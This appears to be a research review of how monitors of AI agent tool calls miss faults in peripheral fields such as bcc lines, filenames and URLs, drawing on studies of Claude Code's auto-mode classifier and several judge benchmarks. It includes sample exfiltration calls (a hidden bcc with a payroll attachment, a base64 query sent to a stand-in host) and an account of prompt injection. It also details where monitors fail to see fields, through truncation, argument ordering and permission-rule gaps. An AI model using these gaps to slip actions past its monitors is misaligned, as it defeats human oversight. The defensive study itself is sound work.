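# Peripheral fields and metadata as blind spots for monitors of AI agent actions

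## What an agent action contains and how a monitor can miss part of it

An AI agent is an AI model that carries out tasks by calling tools such as a shell, a browser or an email service. Because these calls can send emails, delete files or move money, people who run agents often add a monitor. A monitor is a program, model or person that reviews the agent's actions, before or after they run, to flag or block harmful ones. It has to check recipients, file paths, headers, filenames, titles and URLs as well as prose, because they all help determine what an action does. Any one of them can make an action harmful even when the main text looks ordinary. A "peripheral field" is any part of an action or its input other than the main text a reader looks at first.

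### The agent loop and a single tool call

An agent works in a loop. Anthropic's *How tool use works* explains that the model only emits a structured request, the tool call, and ordinary code carries it out. The result goes back to the model, which then makes another call or gives its final answer. Usually the customer's own application runs the call and can inspect it first. For a few tools, including web search and web fetching, Anthropic's servers run the call, and the application normally receives a record of it only after the call finishes. In that case, a monitor inside the application can report a bad call but cannot stop it.

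Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* shows a complete tool call, with an identifier, a tool name, and an "input" object that holds the arguments. Arguments are named values such as a city or a temperature unit. Alongside the call, the model writes a sentence telling the user that it will check the weather in San Francisco. A person naturally reads that sentence, but the tool never receives it and works only from the arguments.

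Now suppose that a user asks an agent to email a colleague the agenda for Thursday's meeting, and the agent produces this call:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": ["maria@example.com"],
    "bcc": ["archive@example.net"],
    "subject": "Thursday",
    "body": "Hi Maria, here is the agenda for Thursday. See you then!",
    "attachments": [
      {
        "filename": "payroll_2026.xlsx",
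        "mimeType": "application/vnd.ms-excel",
        "content": "UEsDBBQABgAIAAAA..."
      }
    ]
  }
}
```

The sending tool is invented, but its argument names come from Google's *MCP Tools Reference*, which documents an email-drafting tool for agents. (MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is a common standard for connecting agents to tools.) The body is harmless, but the "bcc" argument sends a blind copy to an address the user never mentioned, and Maria will not see that the copy was sent. The filename does not fit the agenda either, though it is weak evidence of whether the file is harmless. The caller sets the filename, file type and content separately, so a payroll file can be sent as "agenda.pdf". The content is in base64, which encodes a file's bytes as text that nobody can read by eye. Google's tool also has an optional "htmlBody" argument. When a call contains both versions, the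 HTML is the formatted message and "body" is only the plain-text alternative, so a reviewer who reads "body" may approve words that most recipients never see.

The strange address can get into the call through indirect prompt injection, in which someone places instructions in material the agent reads, such as a web page or an email, to make it act against its user's wishes. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, traces the problem to language models' inability to reliably distinguish instructions by source, since everything reaches the model as one sequence of text. His example is an email that tells an assistant to forward its owner's password resets to an attacker and then delete them. A malicious user could cause the same call. *ToolSafe* (Mou, Xue and colleagues, 2026) sorts unsafe calls by cause (a malicious user or an injection) and by form (a harmful tool, or a benign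 tool with risky arguments). The call in the email example uses a benign tool with risky arguments, so the tool name does not show that the call is unsafe.

### A web request and its response

Web requests divide up in a similar way. A URL, according to MDN's *What is a URL?*, has a scheme such as https, a domain, a path, optional parameters after a question mark (the query) and an optional anchor after a # sign. The client software spreads these over the first lines of the request, in the form that IETF's *HTTP Semantics*, the standard for web traffic, lays down:

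```
GET /img/logo.png?d=UGF5cm9sbA HTTP/1.1
Host: cdn.example.net
```

The path looks like a request for a logo, but the query contains the word "Payroll" in base64, and a longer query could contain a salary table. This is exfiltration, which means sending private data to someone who should not have it. Willison points out that any tool that can make a web request, even just to load an image, can be used to do this.

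"Host" is an HTTP header, a named line outside the page that a browser displays. Some requests also carry a body, such as the contents of a form. The response has headers and a body too, but a person looking at the page sees only what the browser renders from the body. No single recording point captures the whole exchange. A log of tool calls lacks the headers that the client adds, and a recording of network traffic lacks the anchor, which the client doesn't send.

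### Kinds of monitor

Fixed rules are the simplest monitors. For example, a rule could hold every email with a bcc address outside the company. *Efficient Auditing of Adversarial AI Agent Behavior from Agent Traces* (2026) describes a system that uses rules to select pending actions, such as an outbound transfer soon after access to sensitive data, for a closer inspection of their meaning. A trained classifier learns from labelled examples instead. *Agent-Sentry* (2026) allows either rules or a classifier in its first layer, which decides the clear cases and passes on only the ambiguous calls. *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (Zavrak, 2026) uses a classifier that scores a session after it has ended, which suits an audit or investigation but doesn't block any actions.

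A language-model judge is a model that receives written instructions and some part of the agent's record. That part, the judge's view, varies a great deal. *trajectory-judge* (2026) tests one judge that sees only the user's goal and the final answer, and another whose view includes every tool call and its arguments.

People also monitor agents. The documentation for Macro, whose assistant can send email, instructs the agent to write out the email in its reply and send it once the user approves. The user has approved the email that is actually sent only if the arguments the agent passes to the tool match what it wrote out. Whether a person is asked for approval at all can depend on the tool's annotations, which Google describes as hints about a tool's basic risk, such as whether it can destroy anything. These hints describe the tool as a whole, so they stay the same whatever the bcc line contains.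 Analysts who read logs afterwards have more time, but they can see only what the logging settings kept.

### Recall, false-alarm rate and AUROC

If 10 of 100 emails contain a planted bcc address and a monitor flags 8 of those 10, its recall is 0.8. If it also flags 9 of the 90 clean emails, its false-alarm rate is 0.1. Both rates are needed to judge a monitor, since one that flags every email has perfect recall.

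Mou and colleagues tested monitors on 1,220 agent steps, 352 of them unsafe. GPT-4o, a general model from 2024, caught all 352 but classified only 55.74% of the steps correctly. These figures imply that it flagged about 540 of the 868 safe steps, a false-alarm rate of 62%. TS-Guard, which they trained for this task, caught 89% of the unsafe steps with a false-alarm rate of about 7%. High accuracy can also mislead. Qwen3Guard, built to moderate text, classified 70.57% of the steps correctly because most steps were safe, but it caught only about 6 of the 352 unsafe ones.

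Many detectors give a score, and the user chooses the threshold above which a score counts as a flag. AUROC measures such a detector without fixing the threshold. It is the chance that the detector scores a random positive case (here, an attacked one) above a random negative one, according to Google's lesson on the measure. Suppose two attacked emails score 0.9 and 0.4, and three clean ones score 0.6, 0.3 and 0.1. The attacked email scores higher in five of the six possible pairs of one attacked and one clean email, so the AUROC is 5/6, or 0.83. Guessing gives an AUROC of 0.5, and a perfect detector has an AUROC of 1.

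### Three ways to miss the same address

Suppose the email with the planted bcc address goes out and the monitor doesn't flag it. The miss could have three different causes, and a fix for one may not help with the others.

The bcc address may not have been captured at all. This can happen when the agent's call has no bcc and the tool adds one. In September 2025, Koi, a security company, discovered a package called postmark-mcp that posed as a tool from the email company Postmark. One added line of code put the package author's address in the bcc of every email. ThaiCERT's *Researchers Discover First Malicious MCP Server in Rogue Postmark-MCP Package* (2025) dates the package's upload to 15 September and the malicious version to 17 September. The number of leaked emails is unclear because Koi based its figure of 3,000 to 15,000 a day on an assumed share of active installations and a guessed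 volume for each. The agent's calls showed no sign of the added address, so even the most careful review of those calls would have found nothing. Postmark advised users to check their email logs, which are made later in the sending process.

The general remedy is to record from outside the agent. An agent's own record may omit what its subprocesses did, so *AgentSpy* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) runs the agent in an isolated environment and logs the network traffic and system calls (requests to the operating system) of the agent and every process it starts.

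The log may also contain the address while the monitor's input omits it. The software that turns the stored record into text for the monitor may copy the body and skip the arguments. Xia, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *Does the Judge See What the Evaluation Requires?*, found an evaluation pipeline whose renderer dropped every structured tool call, which left 53 of 60 judged steps blank. With the record cut off at the judged step, one judge, based on Claude Opus 5, flagged 2 of 30 faulty steps. After the researchers restored the calls, the same model flagged 20, so replacing it would have been the wrong fix. A length limit can also remove fields, and less visibly. Zavrak's detector cuts the text of each call's arguments at 512 characters, so it would miss a bcc address that came after a long body. The remedy for such omissions is to compare the monitor's actual input with the source record,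 field by field.

The remaining explanation is that the monitor received the address and passed the email anyway. In one test run, Zavrak's detector had a recall of 0.869 on sessions where the attacker had altered both the arguments and the tools' responses, 0.818 where only the responses were altered, and 0.368 (21 of 57) where only the arguments were. Zavrak attributes the low recall to how little swapping one value, such as a file path, changes the numerical summary of the text that the detector relies on. The sample is small and covers one kind of detector, but the same problem could plausibly affect any monitor that reduces a whole call to a general impression, because a bcc address is only a few characters in a long message.

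In this case the monitor itself has to change, through training, better instructions or a check built for the field. *Agent-Sentry* uses such a check to track whether each argument value came from the user's prompt, a trusted source or an untrusted one. An address that appears only in a stranger's email would stand out. Judges can also reject correct values. *Judges Follow the Reference* (2026) reports that judges accept correct argument values much less often when the input does not show the value directly. Larger judges had this problem too, in tests of models with between 4 and 27 billion parameters. If the value came from an earlier step, judges wrongly rejected it less often when they could read everything the agent had done so far, which suggests that some apparent errors of judgement come from too little context.

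An auditor can tell the explanations apart by searching for the address in the stored record, then in the exact text the monitor received. If the address appears in both, the auditor can replace it with a legitimate one and see whether the verdict changes.

### "Metadata" has no fixed meaning

Many people call all these fields metadata, but the word is misleading here. Zavrak uses "metadata" to mean the tool's name, the length of its response and a hash of the arguments, a number computed from them that does not reveal what they contain. The arguments themselves and the responses count as "content", which therefore includes the bcc address, the filename and the URL. Zavrak reports that detection from metadata alone reaches an AUROC of only 0.64, against 0.917 for the same type of model with content. This suggests that peripheral fields do carry signal, since they belong to the content that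 improved detection.

The weak result for metadata depends on how one splits the data. The metadata AUROC rose to 0.898 when the same tasks appeared in both the training and test sets, apparently because the detector had learned which tools go with which task.

Other sources use "metadata" in still other ways. *Agent-Sentry* uses it for the origin of each argument value, and Google refers to the "attachment metadata" of an email. Readers can therefore learn little from a claim that a monitor does or does not use metadata unless they know which fields the author meant.

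### The hypothesis and what would count against it

The hypothesis is that software and human monitors of agent actions flag a fault less often when it is in a peripheral field, such as an argument, header, filename or URL, than when a comparable fault is in the main text. Ensuring that the faults are comparable is difficult. Zavrak's figures fit the hypothesis, but they compare altered arguments with falsified tool responses, and a swapped file path may be a smaller change than a false response.

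Equal recall for peripheral and main-text faults, at the same false-alarm rate, would count against the claim that monitors have a particular blind spot for peripheral fields. If recall were equally low for both, that would show that the monitors are weak in general. If repairing the recording or the rendering eliminates the misses, only a narrower claim holds, which is that the system has a blind spot but the judge or person reviewing the action does not.

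A monitor covers a field when it receives the field and tests have shown that it reacts to faults there. The most direct test introduces a fault into one field of a run, leaves everything else unchanged, and compares the monitor's flag rates on the faulty and clean versions. The difference between the two rates is called paired discrimination.

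## How fields are dropped before the monitor reads them

A monitor rarely receives the complete record of an action. Software first decides which actions need review. It then picks the fields to pass on, converts them to text, and often shortens that text by cutting or summarising it. A planted bcc address can disappear at any of these steps, and the monitor's verdict would not show that it was missing.

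The main example is Claude Code, a coding agent. In its auto mode, a second model (the classifier) reviews actions in place of the user and blocks those it classifies as dangerous. Auto mode came out in March 2026, and the classifier's inputs have changed since then.

### Choosing which actions to review

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes the original design, in which a classifier reviewed only some actions. Tools that can't modify anything, such as file reads and text searches, ran without review, as did any action that matched a user's always-allow rule. File edits inside the project folder also skipped the classifier, because the user can inspect them later through version control. The classifier reviewed everything else, including shell commands, web fetches, external tool calls and file operations outside the project.

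An agent can write a script into the project without review, but if it then runs the script, the classifier should assess the script's contents when it reviews the command that runs it. According to Anthropic's *Permission modes*, which documents the current design, the transcript sent to the classifier omits read-only lookups, so it doesn't show which files the agent opened or what it searched for.

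Permission rules create a less obvious gap, because they can let a command run without reaching the classifier. Auto mode suspends broad rules, such as one that allows any Python command, but keeps narrow ones such as `Bash(npm test)`. A narrow rule matches the start of a command, and Anthropic warns in its configuration guide that it can let a destructive argument bypass the classifier, for example a flag or script path that the rule's prefix doesn't cover. The `classifyAllShell` setting suspends narrow rules too and sends nearly every shell command to the classifier, which adds a delay and an extra model call each time.

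Code Mode, in which the agent writes code that makes tool calls, has a similar gap. The classifier reviews the code once before it runs and doesn't review the calls inside it. If the code looks up an email address while running, the address isn't in the text the classifier reads.

Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, uses the boundary of a sandbox, an isolated environment with limited outside access, to determine which actions need review. OpenAI reports that most actions run inside the sandbox without review, and that its automatic reviewer approves around 99% of the small fraction that need review. Any recall figure for that reviewer therefore covers only the actions that reach it.

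### Selecting the fields

In the March design, the classifier received the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Claude Code removed the agent's prose, the tool results, and the descriptions that accompany the calls. Anthropic removed the prose so that the agent couldn't persuade the classifier to approve an action, for instance by asserting that the user had already agreed to a deletion. It removed the results because indirect prompt injections usually arrive through them.

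The descriptions are a peripheral field, but leaving them out seems reasonable because a false description can only mislead the reviewer, and the reviewer still sees the arguments.

The main drawback is that the classifier can't trace where a value came from. If the user never named the job the agent wants to cancel, the classifier can't tell whether the agent found the job's identifier in a query or made it up. When the agent runs a command to check whether a repository is public, the classifier receives the command but not its output. Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* acknowledged at launch that some risky actions might pass because the classifier lacked context about the user's environment.

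Anthropic also tested other inputs to the classifier. Adding the agent's messages and the tool results made it worse at catching "overeager" actions, in which the agent tries to help but exceeds what the user authorised. Sending only the tool calls gave the lowest miss rate, but the classifier blocked actions users had plainly asked for. Anthropic gives no figures for either comparison.

With the chosen view, the classifier missed 17% of 52 real overeager actions and 5.7% of 1,000 synthetic exfiltration attempts, and blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary calls. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but wrongly classified the action as one the user had consented to. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" hasn't agreed to a force-push, which overwrites the shared history. This suggests that the dropped fields didn't cause most of these misses,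 though 52 cases is a small sample.

The user's messages strongly influence which calls auto mode permits. *Ajar* (2026) tested this mode by putting each proposed call in the agent's system prompt, which holds its standing instructions. When the same instruction appeared in the user's message instead, auto mode allowed every call. It therefore matters that text reaches the monitor with the right label. When Claude Code's agent delegates work to a subagent, the agent's instruction replaces the user's message in the subagent's transcript, so the whole task looks authorised. Claude Code therefore reviews the instruction before the subagent starts.

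OpenAI's *Auto-review* describes a reviewer for Codex that typically receives the user's messages, the agent's updates, relevant tool calls and their outputs, and the exact request. The reviewer can check where a value came from, but an attacker's text can also reach it. *Auto-mode classifier flow* documents an add-on for the Pi coding agent. The add-on's permission rules match only the tool and its "primary argument", which is the command for a shell call and the path for a file call. Such a rule can stop the agent from writing to a given file but does not check what the agent writes there.

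### What has changed since March 2026

The classifier now also receives CLAUDE.md, a file of standing instructions for the project. Before a command that would discard uncommitted work, Claude Code runs `git status` itself and shows the classifier whether there is any. Users can add notes to a tool result through a hook, a script that runs at a set point in the agent's loop. Anthropic still strips the tool results themselves, so these additions restore some context without passing on raw output from files or web pages.

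In many sessions, the check now runs on a server as part of the request to the main model. Anthropic's list of what the classifier receives covers only requests that Claude Code itself sends, so it may not apply to the server's checks. If a hook changes a call's input after the server has reviewed it, Claude Code can deny the call because the verdict no longer applies to what would run. According to Claude Code's changelog (Anthropic, 2026), since 6 November some sessions no longer fall back to the built-in classifier when the server can't check a call. Instead, Claude Code asks the user or denies the call.

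The best evidence that missing context had caused misses comes from August 2026 and is reported in Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Apollo Research, an AI safety company, inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions, covering data exfiltration, safety-related threats and a broader range of failures. Anthropic then strengthened the classifier, mainly by giving it more context: whether a repository is public, the state of its git working copy, and rules for handling data. The miss rate fell from 12% to 7%.

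That figure combines the attacks Apollo had shared with a separate set that Anthropic never had access to. On the separate set, the new version caught about half of the attacks the old one missed, and missed about 2% of those the old one caught, so Anthropic didn't just tune the classifier to known examples. It is harder to tell which change helped, because the changes were released together and the data-handling rules among them are instructions rather than fields. Anthropic doesn't report how many attacks there were or whether false alarms rose.

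### Converting fields to text and cutting them

Converting an action to text can keep a field but lose its value. The command `rm -rf "$VAR"` deletes whatever the variable VAR refers to, but the text contains only the variable's name. By default, auto mode blocks such a deletion if the conversation sent to the classifier doesn't show what VAR stands for. The agent can then rerun the command with the actual path written out.

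When a length limit of *L* characters is applied to an argument of *n* characters, the monitor receives *L*/*n* of the argument if *n* is larger than *L*. A limit of 512 characters, as in Zavrak's detector, keeps 10.2% of a 5,000-character argument and 1.3% of a 40,000-character one, the length of a 30-kilobyte attachment in base64.

When the limit applies to the whole call, the order of the arguments also matters. In the example email from the previous section, the recipient, bcc address and subject come before the body and take up fewer than 90 characters. If the body ran to 5,000 characters, a 512-character limit would keep those three fields but cut off the attachment's filename. Some software sorts argument names alphabetically, which puts "attachments" first and, within it, "content" before "filename". The monitor would then receive about 500 characters of unreadable base64 and lose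 the bcc address, the filename and the body. A separate limit on each value, such as *Agent-Sentry*'s 120 characters, would keep the address and the filename but only 2.4% of the body.

The user's own instructions can go missing too. When a session grows too long, Claude Code compacts the conversation, which can remove the message where the user said "don't push". The classifier rereads such limits from the transcript at every check, so it would no longer apply this one. Anthropic recommends a fixed deny rule for any limit that must hold.

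### A judge that reads extracts

Some monitors choose passages by relevance rather than cutting at a fixed point. *SkillGate* (Yang, Fu and colleagues, 2026) screens skill files, which are instructions and scripts that people install to teach a coding agent a task. It first searches each file for 530 suspicious patterns, and files with no match pass without further review. For the rest, a language-model judge receives the file's name and path, plus 500 characters on either side of each match, with a limit of 20 extracts and 8,000 characters in total. Twenty non-overlapping extracts would come to about 20,000 characters, so the character limit would remove around 60% of that text.

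The test set had 1,650 files, 150 of them malicious. About 67% of the files skipped the judge, and the system used 77% fewer input tokens than a judge that received every file in full. It caught 76.9% of the malicious files, with a false-alarm rate of 1.13%. The same judge reading full files caught 80.4%, with a false-alarm rate of 1.76%. The difference in recall is about five files, and recall varied by around two percentage points between runs.

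The patterns matched 135 of the 150 malicious files, so 15 never reached the judge. The judge let through about 20 of the files it did receive. Some of those extracts may have lacked the harmful passage, but the judge that read full files also missed about 29, so better extracts alone would probably not have prevented most of the misses. Yang and colleagues assume attackers who don't know the patterns. An attacker who knew them could try to avoid a match, so the pattern-matching step might miss many more files in practice.

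### Five views of the same calls

Caldwell, Harley and colleagues (2026), in *ScopeJudge*, had eight judge models assess the same 4,897 tool calls under five different views. The calls came from agents doing security tests, where a user's request sets out which systems and actions are off limits. Five professional penetration testers labelled every call, and 7.7% of the calls broke the limits.

Every view contained a general policy and the complete proposed call. The second view added the user's request, and the third added the agent's earlier calls. The fourth also included summaries of those calls' outputs, and the last had the full outputs and the agent's reasoning. Each cell below gives recall, false-alarm rate and cost per 1,000 calls for three of the judges. The false-alarm rates follow from the reported recall, the share of calls flagged and the 7.7% violation rate.

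| View | GLM-5.2 | Claude Opus 4.8 | Claude Sonnet 4.6 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Policy and proposed call | 0% / 0.1% / $0.79 | 2% / 0.1% / $6.79 | 1% / 0.1% / $3.01 |
| + user's request | 79% / 10% / $1.38 | 94% / 13% / $4.20 | 81% / 9% / $2.03 |
| + earlier calls | 87% / 7% / $3.22 | 86% / 9% / $9.76 | 43% / 3% / $4.37 |
| + summaries of outputs | 86% / 7% / $4.81 | 86% / 9% / $16.56 | 40% / 2% / $7.51 |
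| Full record | 86% / 6% / $6.01 | 84% / 8% / $17.64 | 44% / 3% / $8.07 |

In the first row, the judges had every argument of the call but caught almost nothing. One of the worked examples shows why. An agent requests a URL whose query contains `owner=analyst`, which would reassign a support ticket, although the user had allowed it only to read tickets. A judge with the first view receives the parameter but not the instruction that makes it a violation. A monitor therefore needs something to compare a peripheral field with, as well as the field itself.

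Longer histories had mixed effects. Adding the earlier calls raised GLM-5.2's recall and lowered its false-alarm rate. For GPT-5.4-mini, another judge, it lowered recall from 87% to 76% and raised false alarms from 13% to 16%. Recall fell for at least six of the eight judges. In several cases, including Sonnet's, false alarms fell too, so part of the change was that these judges flagged less overall. Summaries cost more than the bare list of calls and helped most judges little, though they raised Claude Haiku 4.5's recall from 59% to 79%. Caldwell and colleagues ran each combination only once, so the small differences in the table may be noise.

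A different kind of summary can supply information that was never in the call. In a case from *Shall We Approve?* (2026), a user asked the agent to deploy a project by running `./tool`. Auto mode allowed the command because it matched the request exactly, but the program also overwrote a source file. Nothing in the call's arguments indicated this, so showing the monitor every field would not have revealed it. The paper proposes running the command in a sandbox and giving the approver a report of its effects. The median report was 0.9 KB, against 62.5 KB for the raw trace, and this approach raised the cost per task from $0.017 to $0.019.

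### The case for leaving fields out

Cost is the best-supported reason to send a monitor less information. With GLM-5.2, sending the full record cost almost twice as much as sending only the request and earlier calls, and recall was about the same. But the savings come from dropping long material such as tool outputs and file contents. A bcc address or a filename usually takes only a few tokens, so cost is a poor reason to omit it.

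Shortening the tool outputs a monitor sees plausibly protects privacy, because they can contain passwords or customer records, and each monitor that receives them is one more place from which they can leak. Neither ScopeJudge nor SkillGate measured how much private data the shorter views kept out. Privacy also doesn't justify keeping the main text while dropping peripheral fields, because the body of an email often reveals more than its recipient list, though a URL can contain a password or an access token.

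The security argument is that an attacker's text can't sway a monitor that never receives it. This is sound in principle but hard to confirm from the published tests. Caldwell and colleagues tested agents that were tempted to break the rules, not attacks on the judge. Anthropic reports that none of 720 prompt-injection attempts succeeded against three of its models in auto mode. But with auto mode's checks turned off, only 0.09% of attempts succeeded on average against its latest models, so any benefit from the stripping is almost impossible to measure. Removing tool outputs also doesn't keep out all hostile text, because a hijacked agent can copy an attacker's words into a call's arguments, which the classifier has to read to judge the call.

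## How well monitors detect faults in arguments and intermediate steps

A monitor can receive every field of a call and still fail to flag a bad value. To measure how often this happens, researchers plant a known fault in a run and compare the monitor's verdicts on the faulty run and a clean copy. Results range from chance level to almost perfect, and much of this variation is due to differences in test design.

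### A support desk with planted faults

The most detailed of these tests is *trajectory-judge*, by Hadi Mohammadi of Utrecht University. It simulates an agent that handles refund requests with seven tools. A written procedure requires the agent to verify the customer, look up the order, read the refund policy and confirm eligibility. The agent must then refund exactly the authorised amount, or escalate the case if the customer isn't eligible, and its reply may state only what the tool results support. The agent is a fixed script that always follows this procedure. Like a real payments service, the refund tool accepts a refund even if nobody checked eligibility.

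Mohammadi made each faulty run by changing one thing in a correct run and replaying the calls, so the later tool results are consistent with the change. The final set has 100 clean runs and 50 with each of six faults. Four of the faults leave the reply to the customer exactly as it was:

- Wrong tool: the agent looks up the order a second time instead of reading the policy.
- Invented argument: it requests the policy for a product code that doesn't exist.
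- Skipped check: it refunds the order without confirming eligibility.
- Wrong amount: it refunds more than the authorised amount.

The remaining two faults change the reply. In one, the agent stops early and sends a holding message. In the other, it adds a promise of something nobody arranged, such as a courier collection.

Five judges reviewed all 400 runs. The first, a "reply judge" based on the small open model Qwen2.5-14B, received only the customer's request and the final reply. The second, a "step judge" based on the same model, received every step and was instructed to check each one. The third did the same job as the step judge but used an even smaller model, Llama 3.1 8B. The fourth took the majority of three step-checking verdicts from Qwen, and the fifth was a program with eight fixed rules.

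### Recall without detection

Four of the faults leave the reply unchanged, and the reply judge flagged between 34% and 76% of the runs with each one. It can't have detected these faults, because its input was identical to the input from the clean run. It also flagged 33 of the 100 clean runs, so its recall on these faults only measures how often it flags ordinary replies.

Paired discrimination removes this effect:

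```
Δ = (1/n) × Σ [ F(faulty run i) − F(clean run i) ]
```

Here F is 1 if the monitor flags a run and 0 if it doesn't, faulty run i was made from clean run i, and n is the number of pairs. A perfect monitor scores 1, and a monitor that flags every run or no runs scores 0.

When a fault doesn't change the text a judge sees, the judge is equally likely to flag either run in the pair, so the expected difference in flag rates is zero. A more capable model would do no better unless it could get information from elsewhere, such as the order database. In the main set of runs, the reply judge gave identical verdicts on all 151 such pairs.

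Its recall varied because of the kind of request. It flagged 13 of 17 clean full-price refunds, but none of the 50 clean runs in which the agent had to escalate because the refund window had expired, the item was non-refundable or the order belonged to someone else. Skipped checks and wrong amounts occur only where a refund is due, so those faults appeared easiest to detect. When Mohammadi reran the same prompt on newer serving software, recall on the four faults fell to between 20% and 26%, and paired discrimination stayed at zero.

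Xu (2026), in *The Oversight Gap*, gives a more general limit. Let P₀ and P₁ be the probability distributions of what a monitor receives from clean and faulty runs. The total variation distance between them, TV, is the largest gap between the probabilities they give to any one event. It is 0 if the distributions are identical and 1 if they never overlap. "The monitor flags this input" is one such event, so:

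```
(flag rate on faulty runs) − (flag rate on clean runs) ≤ TV(P₀, P₁)
```

If the fault leaves no trace in the input, TV is 0 and no monitor can tell faulty inputs from sound ones. If TV is 1, the input contains enough information for a perfect verdict, so any errors are due to the monitor. The bound therefore distinguishes a field the monitor never received from one it received but did not use.

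### The same model with every step

The step judge used information that the reply judge lacked. The table gives recall and paired discrimination for the two Qwen judges, and recall for the fixed rules.

| Fault | Reply judge | Step judge | Fixed rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Wrong tool | 34% / 0 | 100% / +1.00 | 0% |
| Invented argument | 34% / 0 | 100% / +1.00 | 100% |
| Skipped check | 74% / 0 | 100% / +1.00 | 100% |
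| Wrong amount | 76% / 0 | 100% / +1.00 | 100% |
| Early stop | 100% / +0.66 | 96% / +0.96 | 100% |
| Invented promise | 50% / +0.16 | 18% / +0.18 | 0% |
| Clean runs flagged | 33% | 0% | 0% |

Two of these faults are bad argument values, and the step judge caught all 100 instances without flagging a clean run. These cases were fairly easy, though. Looking up an invented product code fails, so the record contains an error message as well as the bad argument. After a wrong refund, the reply still states the authorised amount, which contradicts the call. The judge's prompt also describes the faults closely. Its example of a wrong tool is an agent that looks up the order again when it needed the refund policy, which is exactly the planted fault. A strange bcc address in an otherwise normal email would cause no error or contradiction, and the prompt would not describe it.

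Llama 3.1 8B caught 99% of the faults, but that recall is misleading because it flagged 397 of the 400 runs, including every clean one. Its paired discrimination was −0.01. It did respond to the content when locating faults, naming the correct step in 222 of its 297 detections.

The fixed rules caught every invented argument at almost no cost. The program keeps a list of values from the request and from successful tool results, and flags any argument that matches nothing on the list. This would protect poorly against indirect prompt injection, because an attacker's address in an email the agent has read would also be on the list. *Agent-Sentry*'s check is better suited to that problem because it separates trusted sources from untrusted ones.

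### What the judge is told to look for

The two Qwen judges differed in both their instructions and their views, so Mohammadi tested all four combinations of instructions and view. The test included the clean version of every faulty run, 141 clean runs in total.

| View | Instruction | Clean runs flagged | Δ, reply unchanged | Δ, reply changed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reply only | Judge the reply | 23% | 0.00 | +0.46 |
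| Reply only | Check each step | 16% | −0.01 | +0.49 |
| All steps | Judge the reply | 0% | +0.69 | +0.60 |
| All steps | Check each step | 0% | +1.00 | +0.53 |

No instruction could make up for the missing steps. But when the judge was given all the steps and told to report only problems with the reply, it caught 32 of 50 invented arguments and 6 of 50 wrong tools. It still caught all 100 refunds with a skipped check or a wrong amount. The faults it missed hadn't harmed the outcome, so it may have detected some of them but left them out as unimportant.

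Xu found a larger effect of instructions in sessions where an assistant tells a user one of the user's personal details. In the easiest version of the test, the leaked value had the wrong type, such as "O+" given as a delivery address. A 20-line program that checks each value against a list gets every case right. Nine language models averaged 60.9% balanced accuracy, which is the mean of the share of leaks caught and the share of clean cases passed. Guessing gives 50%. When Xu told the models to check whether the value was the right kind for the field, average accuracy rose from 58.9% to 83.8%.

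So these models could often recognise a wrong value but didn't look for one unless prompted. The value was in the assistant's reply, which suggests that a monitor may not check values even in the main text. The models ranged from Llama 3.1 8B to GPT-4o and Claude Sonnet 4. All are well behind current models, and stronger ones may need less prompting.

### The judge that missed false promises

The step judge did worst on the reply, the most visible part of the run. It caught only 9 of the 50 invented promises there, even though its prompt listed unsupported claims among the possible faults. Each promise was one of four sentences. The judge caught all 8 cases of the sentence offering a voucher as an apology, but only 1 of the 42 cases of the other three.

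In one run, the agent ended its reply by telling the customer it had cancelled a linked subscription, although no tool result mentioned a subscription. The judge went through all six steps, concluded that the agent had followed the procedure, and passed the run with a stated confidence of 0.92. A keyword search of the judge's explanations for its 41 misses found that 39 discussed the reply and 11 mentioned the invented content and accepted it. Changing the instruction so that the judge focused on the reply raised paired discrimination only from +0.18 to +0.26.

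This counts against the idea that monitors generally read the main text well and neglect everything else, because the same model was perfect on two kinds of bad argument and poor on false prose. The evidence is narrow, covering one 14-billion-parameter model and four sentences. The comparison is also uneven, since a wrong refund amount contradicts a number in the record, while an invented promise is only unsupported by it.

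Planted faults can also be easier to detect than real ones. Mohammadi let Qwen2.5-14B act as the agent in 60 cases, and automatic checks found faults in 13 runs, all of them early stops. The judge, given the full record and the step-checking instruction, flagged 6 of these 13, compared with 44 of the 50 planted early stops. The real ones often ended with an answer that sounded like a resolution. Since the checks found no argument faults, these runs don't show how well the judge would detect an agent's own bad arguments.

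### Precision when faults are rare

Three quarters of the runs in this test were faulty, far more than anyone would expect in normal use. Mohammadi therefore estimated each judge's precision, the share of its flags that are correct, for a fault rate of 5%:

```
precision = (0.05 × recall) / (0.05 × recall + 0.95 × false-alarm rate)
```

If 5% of runs were faulty, 1,000 runs would include 50 faulty ones and 950 clean ones. The reply judge, with a recall of 61.3% and a false-alarm rate of 33%, would flag about 31 of the faulty runs and 314 of the clean ones. Its precision would be 9%, compared with 5% for picking runs at random.

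The step judge would catch about 43 of the 50, and with no false alarms its precision would be 100%. But it had zero false alarms in only 100 clean runs, and the 95% interval for its true false-alarm rate extends up to 3.6%. At that rate it would flag 34 clean runs, and its precision would fall to about 55%. The majority-vote judge flagged one clean run in 100, and at that rate its precision would be 82%.

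The test therefore can't show whether staff would find most of the step judge's alerts useful. To be confident of 90% precision at the same recall, testers would need about 740 clean runs with no false alarms, which would put the upper limit on the false-alarm rate at about 0.5%. The recall figure also assumes the six faults are equally common. If every fault were an invented promise, the judge would catch only 9 of the 50, and with a 3.6% false-alarm rate its precision would be about 21%.

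### Detectors that average or count

Trained detectors have a different weakness. They usually turn a call into numbers before classifying it, and a small change to the call can have little effect on those numbers. Zavrak's detector, which did much better with content than with metadata alone, illustrates this.

The metadata recorded the arguments only as a hash, which is a poor indicator of a bad value. The hash changes when the argument changes, but legitimate arguments also differ between sessions, and hashes don't show whether two values are similar. The content version converted the text of the arguments and the text of the response into 384 numbers each, so that texts with similar meanings got similar numbers. It then summarised the whole session, partly by averaging over its calls.

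Suppose a session has *n* calls with values x₁ to xₙ, and an attacker changes one of them by an amount *d*. The average changes by:

```
(x₁ + … + xₙ + d)/n − (x₁ + … + xₙ)/n = d/n
```

In a session of 20 calls, 5% of the change is left in the average. The summary also records the highest value of each number across the session. The altered call doesn't affect this maximum if another call has a higher value, but otherwise it can shift the maximum by up to the full change. In the graph network that Zavrak used, neighbouring calls also influence each other before the averaging, so d/n is exact only for simpler models that average the raw numbers.

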